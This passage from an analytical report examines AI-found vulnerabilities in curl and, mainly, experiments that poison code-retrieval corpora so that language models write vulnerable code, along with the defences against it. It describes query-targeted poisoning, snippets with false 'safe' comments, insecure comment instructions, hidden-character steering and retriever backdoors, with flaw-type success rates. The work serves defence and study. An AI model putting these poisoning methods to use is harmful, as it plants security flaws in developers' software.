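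Of the 45 reports, 41 (91 percent) identified a real problem, but only 11 percent identified a vulnerability. The 91 percent is close to the 94 percent that the outside firms had judged valid in other projects. The 11 percent would be somewhat higher under curl's old rules, because the project had recently narrowed its definition of a vulnerability. A report can accurately describe what the code does but be wrong about whether it matters, which often depends on how people use the program.

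Memory checkers could not have settled most of these disputes. By the November reports, curl had confirmed 81 vulnerabilities in 2026 from all sources, and Stenberg estimates that a memory-safe language would have prevented only 14 of them.

### What false and duplicate reports cost

Mozilla's *Behind the Scenes Hardening Firefox with Claude Mythos Preview* notes that asking a model to find a problem in code takes little effort, but responding to a plausible but wrong report takes a lot of time and work. Stenberg stopped paying rewards for reports on curl in January 2026 because so many were worthless and written by AI. By April, he said the junk reports had disappeared. In Elektroniktidningen's *New problem*, he and other maintainers describe a growing number of good reports, more than they can comfortably handle.

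Other projects still received many bad reports. Google stopped accepting submissions to its reward program for open-source flaws on 1 October 2026 after an increase in invalid reports, according to TechRadar's *In open source cybersecurity, AI is kind of a problem*. Help Net Security's *AI is drowning software maintainers in junk security reports* (2026) reports that GitHub began requiring a working demonstration with each submission. This rule filters out many unfounded claims, though it could also exclude a correct warning from someone who understands the flaw but can't trigger it.

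Even correct reports can waste time if they are duplicates. Linus Torvalds complained in May that the Linux kernel's security mailing list had become almost unmanageable because different people were finding the same flaws with the same tools. OpenSSL's security inbox went from about nine messages a month to about 70, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *How Coalitions Are Rallying to Secure Open Source for the AI Era* (2026). The duplicates also suggest that repeated runs of a popular tool, even by different people, add less independent scrutiny than the number of reports implies.

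### A language model as a code reviewer

Curl's developers also use AI tools, alongside human review, to check proposed changes before accepting them. Stenberg says the project would merge worse code without them. An AI model can compare code with its stated purpose and detect when a comment describes something the code does not do, or when the code breaks the rules of a network protocol. It can also detect wrong assumptions about how common libraries work.

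A model can also follow code into other files. Linus Åkesson's winning contest program, for example, looked correct until a reader compared the definitions that two files used. A reviewer looking at a diff may not have time to do this, but a model can do it for every change. It may still fail to recognize a flaw, however. Stenberg has not seen an AI tool report a completely new kind of vulnerability, only new examples of known kinds.

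A model takes names and comments into account, so they can also mislead it, much as they mislead people. In one project in the AI Cyber Challenge, labels in the source code that were not meant to deceive anyone caused crash reports to list the wrong files. The agents patched those files instead of the combined file that the compiler used.

The framing of a request also matters. Models recognized most of their own vulnerable code once researchers asked for a security review. A project's reputation can influence a review too. The Mythos report on curl began by stating that flaws were unlikely in the most heavily tested parts of such a well-examined project. The expectation was reasonable, and the report identified no flaws there, but a human reviewer with the same expectation might have looked less carefully. Researchers have also had some success in deliberately misleading model reviewers.

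### Finding a flaw and certifying that there is none

A system can show that a program has a flaw by finding one input that triggers it, but to show that the program has none, it must rule out every possible input. The AI Cyber Challenge tested a similar problem by giving teams 13 warnings from a static analyzer, eight correct and five false. Three teams relied mainly on matching each warning to a proof that their own system had found. They could confirm correct warnings this way but could not reject false ones, because the lack of a proof might only mean that the search had failed. Two teams that relied on a model's judgment gave verdicts on all 13 warnings; one got ten right and the other nine.

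The size of the target also strongly affects whether a run finds anything. Suppose a model has a 2 percent chance of noticing any particular flaw in one run. If a large program contains 100 such flaws and the chances are independent, a single run will find at least one of them about 87 percent of the time (1 − 0.98¹⁰⁰). If a short piece of code contains one such flaw, a single run will miss it 98 percent of the time. The first result would look more impressive, but the model is equally good in both cases. A hundred independent runs on the short piece would find its flaw about 87 percent of the time, but runs of the same model, like reviewers on the same team, may all miss a flaw for the same reason.

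A clean result also goes out of date quickly. The May scan of curl found one confirmed vulnerability and reported no memory errors. *Twenty-two pending curl vulnerabilities* (Stenberg, 2026) explains that in October curl's developers prepared a release with fixes for 22 vulnerabilities and brought it forward because one was serious. Some may have been in code written after May, but the developers could not have relied on the earlier scan to show that curl was safe.

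A short piece of code is also harder to certify because it often can't run without the rest of its program. The AI Cyber Challenge left five projects out of the scoring because they had no harness. The code's safety may also depend on what surrounds it. A function that copies as many bytes as its caller requests is dangerous unless every caller checks the number first. A tool such as Frama-C can prove that certain errors are impossible, but the proof depends on assumptions about how other code will use the function, and copying the function into a new project may violate those assumptions.

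## Experiments with poisoned examples in code retrieval

AI coding assistants retrieve examples from collections that contain many short functions without the programs they came from. When two studies added poisoned examples to such a collection, language models wrote vulnerable code much more often. But the models also wrote a good deal of vulnerable code when every example was safe, so the increase is a better measure of poisoning's effect than the total.

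### How an assistant picks its examples

A developer's request to the assistant is the query. A program called a retriever compares it with every entry in the corpus and passes the most similar entries, often one to five, to the model.

Older retrievers, such as BM25, score an entry by the words it shares with the query. Newer ones use an embedding model, which turns any text into a long list of numbers called a vector. Its training gives texts with similar meanings vectors that point in similar directions. For a query vector q and an entry vector c, the retriever calculates

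similarity = (q · c) / (|q| × |c|)

The top line multiplies the two vectors number by number and adds up the results, and dividing by the bottom line cancels out their lengths. The similarity is 1 if the vectors point in the same direction and close to 0 if the texts have nothing in common. Some systems then use a slower model, a re-ranker, to compare the query with each of the best candidates and reorder them.

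This calculation measures what the code is about, which is usually the same for a safe function and a vulnerable one. *CoQuIR* (Geng, Cai and colleagues, 2025) gives the example of two functions that create a pair of encryption keys. One defaults to 2,048-bit keys and the other to 1,024-bit keys, which are too short to be secure. A request for a function that creates a key pair describes both equally well.

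Geng and his colleagues tested 23 retrievers on queries that each had a safe and a vulnerable answer. Random ranking would place the safe answer higher half the time. On 1,267 pairs from one collection, a large OpenAI embedding model ranked the safe answer higher 47.6 percent of the time, and the best retriever, Voyage-code-3, 57.5 percent. On a second collection, the figures were 64.5 and 69.6 percent. But a language model had written those queries by summarizing the repaired code, which may have made the safe version a slightly better match. Some retrievers accept instructions, but telling them to prefer high-quality code made almost no difference.

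### Attackers who know the request and attackers who don't

*Exploring the Security Threats of Knowledge Base Poisoning in Retrieval-Augmented Code Generation* (Lin, Chen and colleagues, 2025) used 12,053 functions from real projects in C, C++, Java and Python. Each function had a vulnerable version, a repaired version and a description of its purpose. The repaired versions formed the clean corpus, the descriptions served as queries, and the vulnerable versions supplied the poisoned examples.

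In the first scenario, the attacker knows what the developer will ask for, perhaps from a project's public plans. The researchers added the one to nine vulnerable functions that best matched each query. In the second, the attacker doesn't know the queries but can see the corpus. The researchers sorted the corpus into groups of similar functions, picked the most typical members of each group, and added the vulnerable function closest to each pick. They varied the number of picks from 20 to 100 percent of the corpus.

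They tested four models with one retrieved example per query. The table shows the percentage of generated functions they counted as vulnerable when they used JINA, an embedding-based retriever.

| Model | No poisoning | Known query, 1 example | Known query, 9 examples | Unknown query, 20% | Unknown query, 100% |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 26 | 42 | 47 | 32 | 47 |
| Llama 3 8B | 18 | 34 | 37 | 28 | 38 |
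| Code Llama 13B | 29 | 48 | 53 | 36 | 52 |
| DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B | 25 | 44 | 50 | 32 | 50 |

According to the paper's summary, a single poisoned example can compromise up to 48 percent of the generated code. That figure is for Code Llama, whose baseline was already 29 percent, so poisoning added 19 percentage points. The researchers also chose a separate poisoned example for each query, so the 48 percent reflects the combined effect of many examples.

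But the retriever returned the poisoned example for only 38 percent of queries, and the 48 percent also includes the queries for which it returned a safe one. If Code Llama wrote vulnerable code at its usual rate of 29 percent for those other queries, it must have done so for about 79 percent of the queries that retrieved the poisoned example: (0.48 − 0.62 × 0.29) / 0.38. The same calculation gives 60 percent for Llama 3, the lowest of the four. The retriever therefore seems to have been a bigger obstacle to the attack than the model.

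Lin and his colleagues point out that an attacker who didn't know the queries needed 9,642 poisoned examples for one to be retrieved 35 percent of the time, while an attacker who knew the query reached 38 percent with a single example. The comparison exaggerates the difference, because the 9,642 examples covered all the queries and the single example covered only one. Still, an attacker targeting one kind of request would need very few examples.

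BM25 offered some accidental protection. With one poisoned example per query, it returned that example only 5 percent of the time, and the share of vulnerable code rose by just 3 to 6 percentage points. But BM25 was also bad at finding useful code, ranking the right function first for 14 percent of queries, compared with 79 percent for JINA.

### Flawed examples written to order

Lin's team used vulnerable functions that already existed, and an attacker limited to those can't freely choose both the task and the flaw. In *CodePoisonRAG*, Gadey, Marey and Dmitrienko (2026) instead prepared an example for each task they expected a developer to request. They started with a clean corpus of 12,053 repaired functions from the same source and added 85 poisoned snippets, 65 in Java and 20 in C, covering ten CWE types. Each snippet performed an ordinary task but contained a chosen flaw and a comment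 claiming the code was safe.

Each of the 85 snippets had a matching query, and the model received the three highest-ranked entries for that query. Every snippet ranked in the top three. Code Llama reproduced the chosen flaw in 79 of the 85 cases (93 percent), and Qwen 3.5 9B and DeepSeek-Coder-V2 16B each did so in 68 (80 percent).

For comparison, the researchers replaced the poisoned snippets with safe counterparts and ran Code Llama again. It still produced the flaw in 25 of the 85 cases (29 percent).

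| Type of flaw | With safe counterparts | With poisoned snippets |
|---|---|---|
| Running an outsider's text as program code | 1 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Improper input validation in C | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Using memory outside the reserved area (two types) | 1 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| SQL injection | 2 of 10 | 9 of 10 |
| Fetching any web address an outsider supplies | 4 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Opening files outside the permitted folder | 5 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
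| Putting an outsider's text on a web page unfiltered | 6 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Running an outsider's text as a system command | 3 of 5 | 5 of 5 |
| Rebuilding program objects from untrusted data | 3 of 10 | 5 of 10 |

Poisoning therefore accounts for about 54 of Code Llama's 79 flawed answers. It made the most difference for flaws that the model rarely produced without it. The difference of two cases in the last row could easily be chance. The researchers did not run this comparison on the other two models, so it is unclear how much of those models' 80 percent comes from poisoning.

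The safe counterparts may not have been close matches. On a scale from 0 to 1, Qwen's answers had an average similarity of 0.594 to the poisoned snippets but only 0.169 to the safe functions from which the snippets were made. If the two versions differed by a line or two, as in the paper's illustrations, these scores would be nearly equal. Many snippets must therefore differ from their originals in more than the flaw. A safe example that fitted the query as well as the poisoned one might have reduced the 25 flawed answers further.

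The false comments contributed little, since the attack still succeeded in 77 cases without them. Comments have more influence when they contain instructions. Munir, Quinzan and Roberts (2026), in *Hidden in the Comments*, gave ten small models unfinished code with insecure instructions in the comments, and about 85 percent of the resulting code was vulnerable.

### Whether anyone would notice the snippets

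The researchers report no CodePoisonRAG experiment in which a reviewer or a static analyzer examined the poisoned snippets, and they assumed that the corpus's owner would not inspect every entry by hand. They do argue that the attack is hard to detect from the length of the answers or the time the model takes, because it barely changes either.

Some of the flaws may be fairly easy to find. Many of the snippets pass untrusted input to a dangerous operation within a single function, which is the pattern taint analysis looks for, although analyzers can struggle with code that doesn't compile by itself. The success rates measure how well the snippets influenced models, so they aren't evidence that the flaws were well hidden.

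The researchers tested CodeGuarder, which adds relevant security advice to the model's prompt. It reduced the number of flawed answers from 79 to 60 for Code Llama, from 68 to 51 for DeepSeek-Coder-V2, and from 68 to 34 for Qwen. The advice helped Code Llama write safer code even though 84 of the 85 poisoned snippets still reached its prompt.

### Language models as judges

Both studies used a language model to decide whether the generated code was vulnerable. Lin and his colleagues explain that static analyzers were not practical because a function is hard to compile without the rest of its program, and that checking so many answers by hand would have taken too long.

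The researchers checked a sample of about 360 answers by hand and found that their judge, DeepSeek-V2.5, was right 72 percent of the time for C++ and 84 percent for Python, with C and Java in between. They also tested it on the original pairs of vulnerable and repaired functions. For C, it recognized 72 percent of the vulnerable functions, and its overall accuracy of 80 percent implies that it wrongly flagged about 12 percent of the repaired ones.

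Errors like these raise the baseline, because a model that wrote only safe C would still appear to write vulnerable code 12 percent of the time. They also make the effect of poisoning look smaller. If the true share of vulnerable code rose by 30 percentage points, the share this judge flagged would rise by only 18, or 30 × (0.72 − 0.12), assuming the judge makes the same kinds of mistakes with and without poisoning.

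Such errors may explain a discrepancy in the BM25 results. Since the model saw only one example per query, poisoning could hardly affect an answer unless the retriever returned a poisoned example. With nine poisoned examples available, BM25 returned one for 7 percent of queries. Yet the share of vulnerable code rose by 10 percentage points for Code Llama and 11 for Llama 3. At least three or four of those points probably have another cause, such as random variation in the answers or the judge's verdicts. Differences of a few points in this study are therefore not very meaningful, but most of the increases with JINA are much larger.

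Gadey and his colleagues used GLM-5.1 as their judge, with written rules for each type of flaw. DeepSeek-Coder-V2 also judged Qwen's 85 answers and called them all vulnerable, whereas GLM-5.1 had accepted 17 as safe. With CodeGuarder switched on, the two judges rated 61 and 40 percent of the answers vulnerable. The researchers trusted the larger model's stricter verdicts, but they report no check by human experts. The comparison between 79 and 25 flawed answers is more reliable than either number alone, because the same judge assessed both sets.

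### Vulnerable code without poisoning

Both studies give a baseline of about 29 percent for Code Llama, though this may be a coincidence because they used different queries and judges. The figure would probably be lower for ordinary programming, because every function in the corpus comes from a fix for a real vulnerability, so the queries tend to concern code in which a mistake is dangerous.

Comparisons between models are less consistent. In Lin's study, Code Llama wrote more vulnerable code than Llama 3, and the researchers suggested that models trained mainly on code had learned more vulnerable patterns. *Guiding AI to Fix Its Own Flaws* (2025) reports the opposite order for these two families and found that GPT-4o wrote vulnerable code more often than its predecessor, GPT-3.5. The researchers did not conclude from this that newer models are worse, and it would be hard to rank the models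 from such conflicting results.

Poisoning is also harder to discover when a model often writes vulnerable code from safe examples, because a developer who finds a flaw in its answer has little reason to suspect the corpus.

### A corpus that already contains the answer

In Lin's study, the clean corpus contained a safe answer to every query because the researchers derived the queries from the functions. Where a function had no description, a language model wrote one from the repaired code, and 86 percent of these descriptions were judged accurate in a manual check. Real developers often ask for something that no stored function does exactly. A poisoned example might then face less competition from safe ones, but it might also match the request less closely and have less influence.

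The perfect retrieval rate in CodePoisonRAG also depended on matching queries, but the wording did not have to be exact. When the researchers paraphrased the queries, the retriever still returned all 85 snippets, and Code Llama reproduced 78 of the flaws.

Unrelated requests give a better idea of the wider danger. The system retrieved a poisoned snippet for eight of 50 programming tasks from another benchmark, and six of those eight answers contained the flaw. The researchers did not run these tasks on a clean corpus, but at a baseline of 29 percent, two or three of the eight answers would have been flawed anyway. A poisoned corpus might therefore do little harm to most users but be very dangerous for the few whose requests the attacker anticipated.

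Both experiments also began with the poisoned examples already in the corpus, so they don't show how hard it would be to get such examples into a collection that a company uses, or how long the examples would stay there.

### Whether newer models copy flaws less

Most of the models in these studies are small or date from 2023 and 2024. An experiment with more capable models, reported in *SoK: Understanding (New) Security Issues Across AI4Code Use Cases* (2025), found much less copying. Researchers showed six models, including Claude Sonnet 4, Gemini 2.5 Pro and o3, either the vulnerable or the repaired version of 200 functions. The baseline rate of vulnerable answers was 45 percent, and seeing the vulnerable version increased it by only 1.0 to 5.5 percent, which was not statistically significant.

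The researchers concluded that modern models resist copying flaws from a single example, but their counts look more like a small effect than none. In 287 cases, a model reproduced a flaw only after seeing the vulnerable version. The reverse happened about 187 times, and the researchers treated the two numbers as roughly balanced. Detection errors may also have hidden part of the effect, because the experiment used a language-model prompt to detect flaws, and models were not very good at this in the paper's other tests.

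Sun, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues (2026), in *Coding Agents Propagate Vulnerabilities in Code Bases*, avoided the problem by running known attacks against the finished programs. They tested coding agents, which search a project for useful code themselves instead of receiving examples from a retriever. In one experiment, three agents wrote new web applications next to finished ones they did not need. Compared with having no neighbours, vulnerable neighbours reduced the share of correct and secure applications by 3.4 percentage points on average, while safe neighbours increased it by 4.4 points.

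The effect was much larger when the agents had to rely on existing code. In 20 tasks from real C and C++ projects, five agents filled in a missing piece of a program while the researchers varied whether similar code elsewhere in the project was safe. The agents produced secure solutions 35.4 percentage points less often when that code was vulnerable. The share of secure solutions fell from 91 to 42 percent for the agent using GPT-5.6 Sol, and by at least 25 points for each of the others, including those using GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5.5.

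These models are recent and powerful, so greater ability has clearly not eliminated copying. But the researchers chose tasks with similar code nearby, and an agent has good reason to follow a project's conventions. It might rely less on an outside example. Sun and her colleagues did not study deliberate poisoning, though they expect it to exploit the same tendency. Their two results suggest that the danger depends on how much the model needs the example. If so, retrieval may be riskiest where it is most useful, as with private libraries that the model has never seen.

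Telling the agents to be careful with existing code reduced the difference in the C and C++ tasks but did not remove it. When the researchers asked the agents to review their own vulnerable solutions, the agents identified the flaw in 69.9 percent of cases, so lack of knowledge was often not the problem.

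## Which checks carry over to a retrieval corpus

The coding agents that recognized flaws in their own work had access to a whole project. An entry in a retrieval corpus is usually a single function cut out of its program, and the corpus owner may never have seen the rest. Many of the checks that worked in the earlier cases need something such an entry lacks.

The last column of this table is an inference from how each check works, not a measured result.

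| Check | Where it helped | What it needs | In a corpus of snippets |
|---|---|---|---|
| Comparison with a trusted copy | Linux, 2003 | A record of where the code came from | Works if the owner kept the record |
| Search for hidden characters | Text-direction attacks | The stored text | Works unchanged |
| Compiling, testing and fuzzing | Contests, AI Cyber Challenge | Code that builds | Mostly lost |
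| Measuring a running program | xz Utils | A program to run | Lost until somebody uses the code |
| Review by a maintainer | Minnesota patches | Someone who knows the surrounding code | Lost |
| Taint analysis | Heartbleed, after changes to the tools | A visible path from source to sink | Works if the whole path is in the snippet |
| Prompted review | Zurich experiments | A reader and an instruction | Works, but there are thousands of entries |

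Searching the corpus for hidden characters takes little effort and is worth doing. Gadey and colleagues cite an attack called RAG-Pull, which uses such characters to steer an assistant's search toward malicious code.

### Comparing an entry with its source

BitMover's nightly comparison needed only two copies of a file. The owner of a corpus could run the same check by recording the project and commit each entry came from, then periodically fetching the original and comparing the two. A mismatch would show that somebody had changed the entry after the owner copied it.

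Comparing the corpus with the project's current code could also expose bad entries that nobody had altered. In their poisoning experiments, Lin and colleagues used old versions of real functions that developers had since fixed. An owner who had recorded each function's origin could have found the fix and put the new version in the corpus. A reviewer of a new patch has no corrected version to compare it with.

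Comparing a retrieval corpus with its source doesn't catch code that was already flawed when its author published it. Gadey and his colleagues assume an attacker who puts flawed code in a public repository or dataset and waits for others to copy it. The corpus would then match its source exactly and still contain the flaw, just as reproducible builds from the xz 5.6.0 archive would have matched each other and all contained the backdoor.

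The owner of a retrieval corpus could accept code only from established projects. *ImportSnare* (2025), a study of poisoned documentation that steers models toward an attacker's software libraries, discusses a similar rule for libraries. It says an approved list might work but could further entrench the libraries that already dominate.

Established projects also publish unsafe code. Lin, Wang and colleagues, who ran the poisoning experiments, later examined Java code in CodeSearchNet, a widely used collection of open-source functions (*Give LLMs a Security Course*, 2025). Of 841 pieces of code that used random numbers, 684 (81 percent) generated them with a weak method. This matters only where an attacker would gain from predicting the number, and most of these cases are presumably accidental. But a model can copy an accidental flaw as easily as a planted one, so the corpus owner has reason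 to remove both.

### Code without a program around it

An owner who wants to compile or test a function has to supply the missing parts. Simple stand-ins may make it run, but the test then shows only how the function behaves with the stand-ins. It would be better to build the original project at the recorded commit, run the analyzers there and store their warnings with the entry. This would often fail for older code, much of which no longer compiles.

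The missing context also limits the attacker. Åkesson's contest program and the Minnesota patches depended on code in more than one place. If a model copies only one function, the flaw may stop working. A poisoned example works more reliably if the snippet contains the whole flaw. Gadey and his colleagues built their examples this way, so taint analysis can catch them.

Missing checks are harder to judge. A function may rely on its callers to check how many bytes it copies, but a corpus entry doesn't include those callers. Inside a project, an analyzer that flagged every such function would produce many false positives. A corpus owner can reasonably be stricter, because the model may use the function in a program where nobody checks the length.

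The corpus owner can also act on suspicion alone, whereas the kernel developers refused preventive patches. Changing a kernel function may break something that depends on it, but no program depends on a corpus entry in this way, so the owner can add the missing check or delete the function.

### Reading twelve thousand entries

Corpus entries are often no longer than the code in the Zurich experiments, so telling readers to look for security problems might help about as much as it did there. But the corpus that Gadey's team poisoned had 12,138 entries. At 10 minutes each, one person would need about 2,000 hours, or a working year, to read them all, and using three or four readers per entry would triple or quadruple that.

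The owner could have people read an entry only when the assistant first retrieves it. Lin's team suggests looking for the types of flaw that models are more likely to reproduce. In its experiments, about 79 percent of answers were vulnerable when the assistant retrieved an example that let other websites send commands in a user's name (cross-site request forgery), compared with 36 percent or less when the example accepted dangerous file uploads. These figures have no baseline, so the models may be bad at preventing forged requests even with safe examples.

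A language model can read the whole corpus. The judge in Lin's poisoning experiments is the closest thing to a source of measured error rates for this job. Across the four programming languages, it recognized 72 to 80 percent of the vulnerable functions, and its scores imply that it wrongly flagged 12 to 19 percent of the repaired ones. But the researchers first gave it information about how such flaws arise and how developers fix them, which an owner looking for an unknown flaw may not be able to provide.

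### How many alarms would be real

Even a fairly accurate scanner will mostly raise false alarms if few entries are poisoned. Assume it catches half the poisoned entries and wrongly flags 5 percent of the clean ones. In the corpus above, where 85 entries (0.7 percent) were poisoned, it would flag about 43 poisoned entries and 603 clean ones, so only about one alarm in 15 would be real.

If p is the share of entries that are poisoned, s the share of those that the scanner catches, and f the share of clean entries that it wrongly flags, then the share of alarms that are real is

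p × s / (p × s + (1 − p) × f)

The table shows the result for other rates in the same corpus. The last row applies the judge's measured rates for C to all the entries.

| Poisoned entries caught | Clean entries flagged | Total alarms | Poisoned entries among them | Share that are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | 5% | 645 | 43 | 1 in 15 |
| 90% | 5% | 679 | 77 | 1 in 9 |
| 50% | 1% | 163 | 43 | 1 in 4 |
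| 50% | 20% | 2,453 | 43 | 1 in 58 |
| 72% | 12% | 1,508 | 61 | 1 in 25 |

Flagging fewer clean entries improves the result more than catching more poisoned ones, because there are about 142 clean entries for each poisoned one. If the attacker poisons fewer entries, a smaller share of the alarms will be real. With only five poisoned entries in a corpus of this size, the scanner in the first row would raise about 609 alarms, of which two or three would be real.

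Checking 645 alarms at 10 minutes each would take about 108 hours. The owner could instead delete every flagged entry without checking it, which would remove half the poisoned entries and 5 percent of the clean ones. Deleting clean code this way would make no sense in a kernel, but it may be acceptable in a collection of examples.

Deleting the flagged entries would leave about 42 poisoned entries in the corpus, and the clean entries lost would probably not be a random sample. Scanners tend to flag functions that open files, run commands or query databases, so the corpus would lose many of its examples for tasks where a mistake is dangerous. Repairing or replacing the flagged entries would take longer but keep the corpus useful.

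The calculation also counts every unpoisoned entry as clean. That is roughly right for this corpus, where the other entries are repaired functions. In a collection like CodeSearchNet, many of the alarms counted as false would point to real accidental flaws, so checking them would be a better use of the owner's time than the table indicates.

### Adding a second check

Suppose the owner adds another scanner with the same assumed rates, 50 and 5 percent. The owner can reduce false alarms by acting only on entries that both scanners flag, or catch more poisoned entries by acting on any entry that either scanner flags. The benefit depends on whether the scanners make the same mistakes.

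| Errors of the two scanners | Flagged by both | Flagged by either |
|---|---|---|
| Independent | 51, including 21 poisoned | 1,239, including 64 poisoned |
| Partly shared | 333, including 32 poisoned | 957, including 53 poisoned |
| Identical | 645, including 43 poisoned | 645, including 43 poisoned |

For the middle row, we assume the new scanner flags three quarters of the poisoned entries that the old one flagged, and half the clean ones.

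If the two scanners' errors were independent, two in five entries flagged by both would be poisoned, compared with one in 15 flagged by a single scanner. The new scanner would add nothing if it made the same errors as the first. Two analyzers with similar rules are likely to share many errors, and an attacker who tests a snippet against both can make sure both miss it.

Checks that use different evidence are less likely to fail together. For example, comparing code with the original project can reveal a mismatch whether or not the code looks dangerous. An owner who can run only two checks is therefore probably better off with this comparison and one scanner than with two scanners.

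### Filters tested on poisoned corpora

Researchers have tested some automatic filters on corpora they poisoned themselves. *Exploring the Security Threats of Retriever Backdoors in Retrieval-Augmented Code Generation* (2025) tested three of them against an attack that also tampers with the retriever. Activation clustering, which groups entries by their vectors and looks for a group that stands apart, caught 55 to 75 percent of the poisoned entries, depending on which requests the attack targeted. Spectral signature, which looks for individual entries with unusual vectors, caught none.

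KillBadCode, which looks for words that seem out of place in code, caught between 55 and 70 percent of the poisoned entries. But when the researchers ran it on a corpus with no poisoned entries, it flagged exactly the same words. These were harmless words, none of them the attacker's, and KillBadCode caught poisoned entries only because some happened to contain them.

The researchers measured recall, the share of poisoned entries that a filter catches. Recall does not depend on how many clean entries the filter removes, so a filter that deleted 60 percent of a corpus at random would also have a recall of about 60 percent. The figures for activation clustering are hard to interpret for the same reason. The researchers add that ten poisoned entries are too few for these filters to identify reliably.

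All three filters look for statistical traces of an attack and do not check whether the code is safe. The poisoned examples in the experiments by Lin's and Gadey's teams worked with an ordinary retriever and needed no trigger words, so they would probably leave even fewer traces to detect, though neither team tested such filters.

In *ImportSnare*, researchers tested a language model, DeepSeek-V3, as the filter on the retrieved documents, the complete prompt and the final answer. The model had a low success rate on the documents, partly because not all of them were poisoned, and did better on the complete prompt. The researchers warn that checking everything this way would be expensive at scale. Their poisoned documents recommended a library and did not contain flawed code, so a model might do better or worse at detecting flawed code.

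The assistant could also choose its example differently. Lin and his colleagues propose taking the second-best match, or choosing at random among several good ones, but have not tested either idea. Their results suggest that a looser match would reduce the danger. When the attacker knew the requests, 53 percent of answers were vulnerable if the example was very similar to the request, compared with 28 percent if it was very different.

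Part of that difference arose because close matches were more often poisoned, but a looser match would also be less useful to the developer. An attacker could respond by adding several poisoned examples for the same request. Giving the model more examples did not help either. With the team's embedding-based retriever, the share of vulnerable answers rose from 46 percent with one example to 49 percent with three.

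### Security advice in the prompt

CodeGuarder leaves poisoned entries in the corpus and is meant to counteract them by adding security advice to the prompt. Lin, Wang and their colleagues drew this advice from records of past vulnerabilities. For each one, a language model recorded what the code was for, what caused the flaw and how the developers fixed it. CodeGuarder divides each request into smaller tasks and finds the two most relevant pieces of advice for each task. It then adds only the advice for the five riskiest tasks, judged by how often models make the mistakes in question.

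The researchers tested CodeGuarder with four models on 1,916 programming tasks. The table shows the average share of answers that an automatic detector classified as secure.

| Corpus | Without CodeGuarder | With CodeGuarder |
|---|---|---|
| Clean | 60.8% | 73.1% |
| Attacker knows the requests | 50.6% | 66.5% |
| Attacker does not know the requests | 60.1% | 73.2% |

The paper reports the improvements under poisoning as 31.53 and 21.91 percent. These are relative increases, equivalent to about 16 and 13 percentage points.

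Much of this benefit came from making the models' code safer in general rather than from countering poisoning. When the attacker knew the requests, poisoning reduced the share of secure answers by 10.3 points without CodeGuarder and by 6.6 points with it, so the advice removed about a third of the damage. When the attacker did not know the requests, poisoning reduced the share by less than one point even without CodeGuarder, so that result is little evidence that CodeGuarder defends against poisoning.

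The scores may also overstate how secure the code is. The detector uses fixed pattern rules, and about 96 percent of its warnings are correct, but that figure does not measure how many flaws it misses. CodeGuarder often advises the model to replace a risky function with a safer one, which is the kind of change that scores well under pattern rules. The advice did not make the code less useful, since all four models did as well as before or slightly better on two standard sets of programming problems.

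Results varied by type of flaw. With DeepSeek-V3, CodeGuarder prevented 89 percent of one class of memory errors and 36 percent of SQL injections, but only 8 percent of path traversal flaws and about 5 percent of cross-site scripting flaws. The last figure comes from only 13 cases, all in JavaScript, for which CodeGuarder had no specific advice. An attacker could choose a flaw that the advice does not cover.

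In tests by Gadey and colleagues, Code Llama still gave 60 flawed answers out of 85 with CodeGuarder's advice, but only 25 when safe snippets replaced the poisoned ones. For this model, cleaning the corpus would have helped far more than adding advice, provided somebody could find the poisoned entries. The advice worked better with Qwen, reducing the file-access flaw from seven of 10 cases to two. Code Llama still produced that flaw in eight cases and DeepSeek-Coder-V2 in nine.

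CodeGuarder also increased the average response time from 5.2 to 9.2 seconds and the amount of text processed by about 80 percent. Because it retrieves its advice from its own collection, the owner has a second corpus to protect.

### Checking the answer instead of the example

A system can also check the code that the model writes. *Activating Latent Security Knowledge through LLM-Guided Risk Analysis for Secure Code Generation* (2026) describes PromSec, which revises the prompt until a static analyzer finds few enough weaknesses in the resulting code. According to that paper, PromSec substantially reduced the share of vulnerable code while preserving its intended function. This is evidence about insecure code in general, not about poisoned corpora.

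Each round of analysis takes time. More seriously, repeating the process until the warnings stop favours code that triggers no warnings, which may be safe or may contain a kind of flaw the analyzer misses.

Checking the answer has a large advantage over checking the example. Once a developer puts the code into a project, it has callers again, and usually a build, tests and colleagues who know the surrounding program. A reviewer can then find out whether any code checks the number of bytes before the function copies them.

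The disadvantage is that each project's reviewers have to find the flaw themselves. Suppose a poisoned example reaches ten projects, and each has one prompted reviewer with a 54 percent chance of noticing the flaw, as in the Zurich experiment. If the chances are independent, an average of 4.6 reviewers will miss it, and the probability that all ten catch it is about 0.2 percent (0.54¹⁰).

But at least one of the ten will almost certainly catch it (1 − 0.46¹⁰, or more than 99.9 percent). If the assistant recorded which entries it retrieved for each answer, that reviewer could trace the flaw to the corpus. The owner could then delete the entry and warn the other nine projects.
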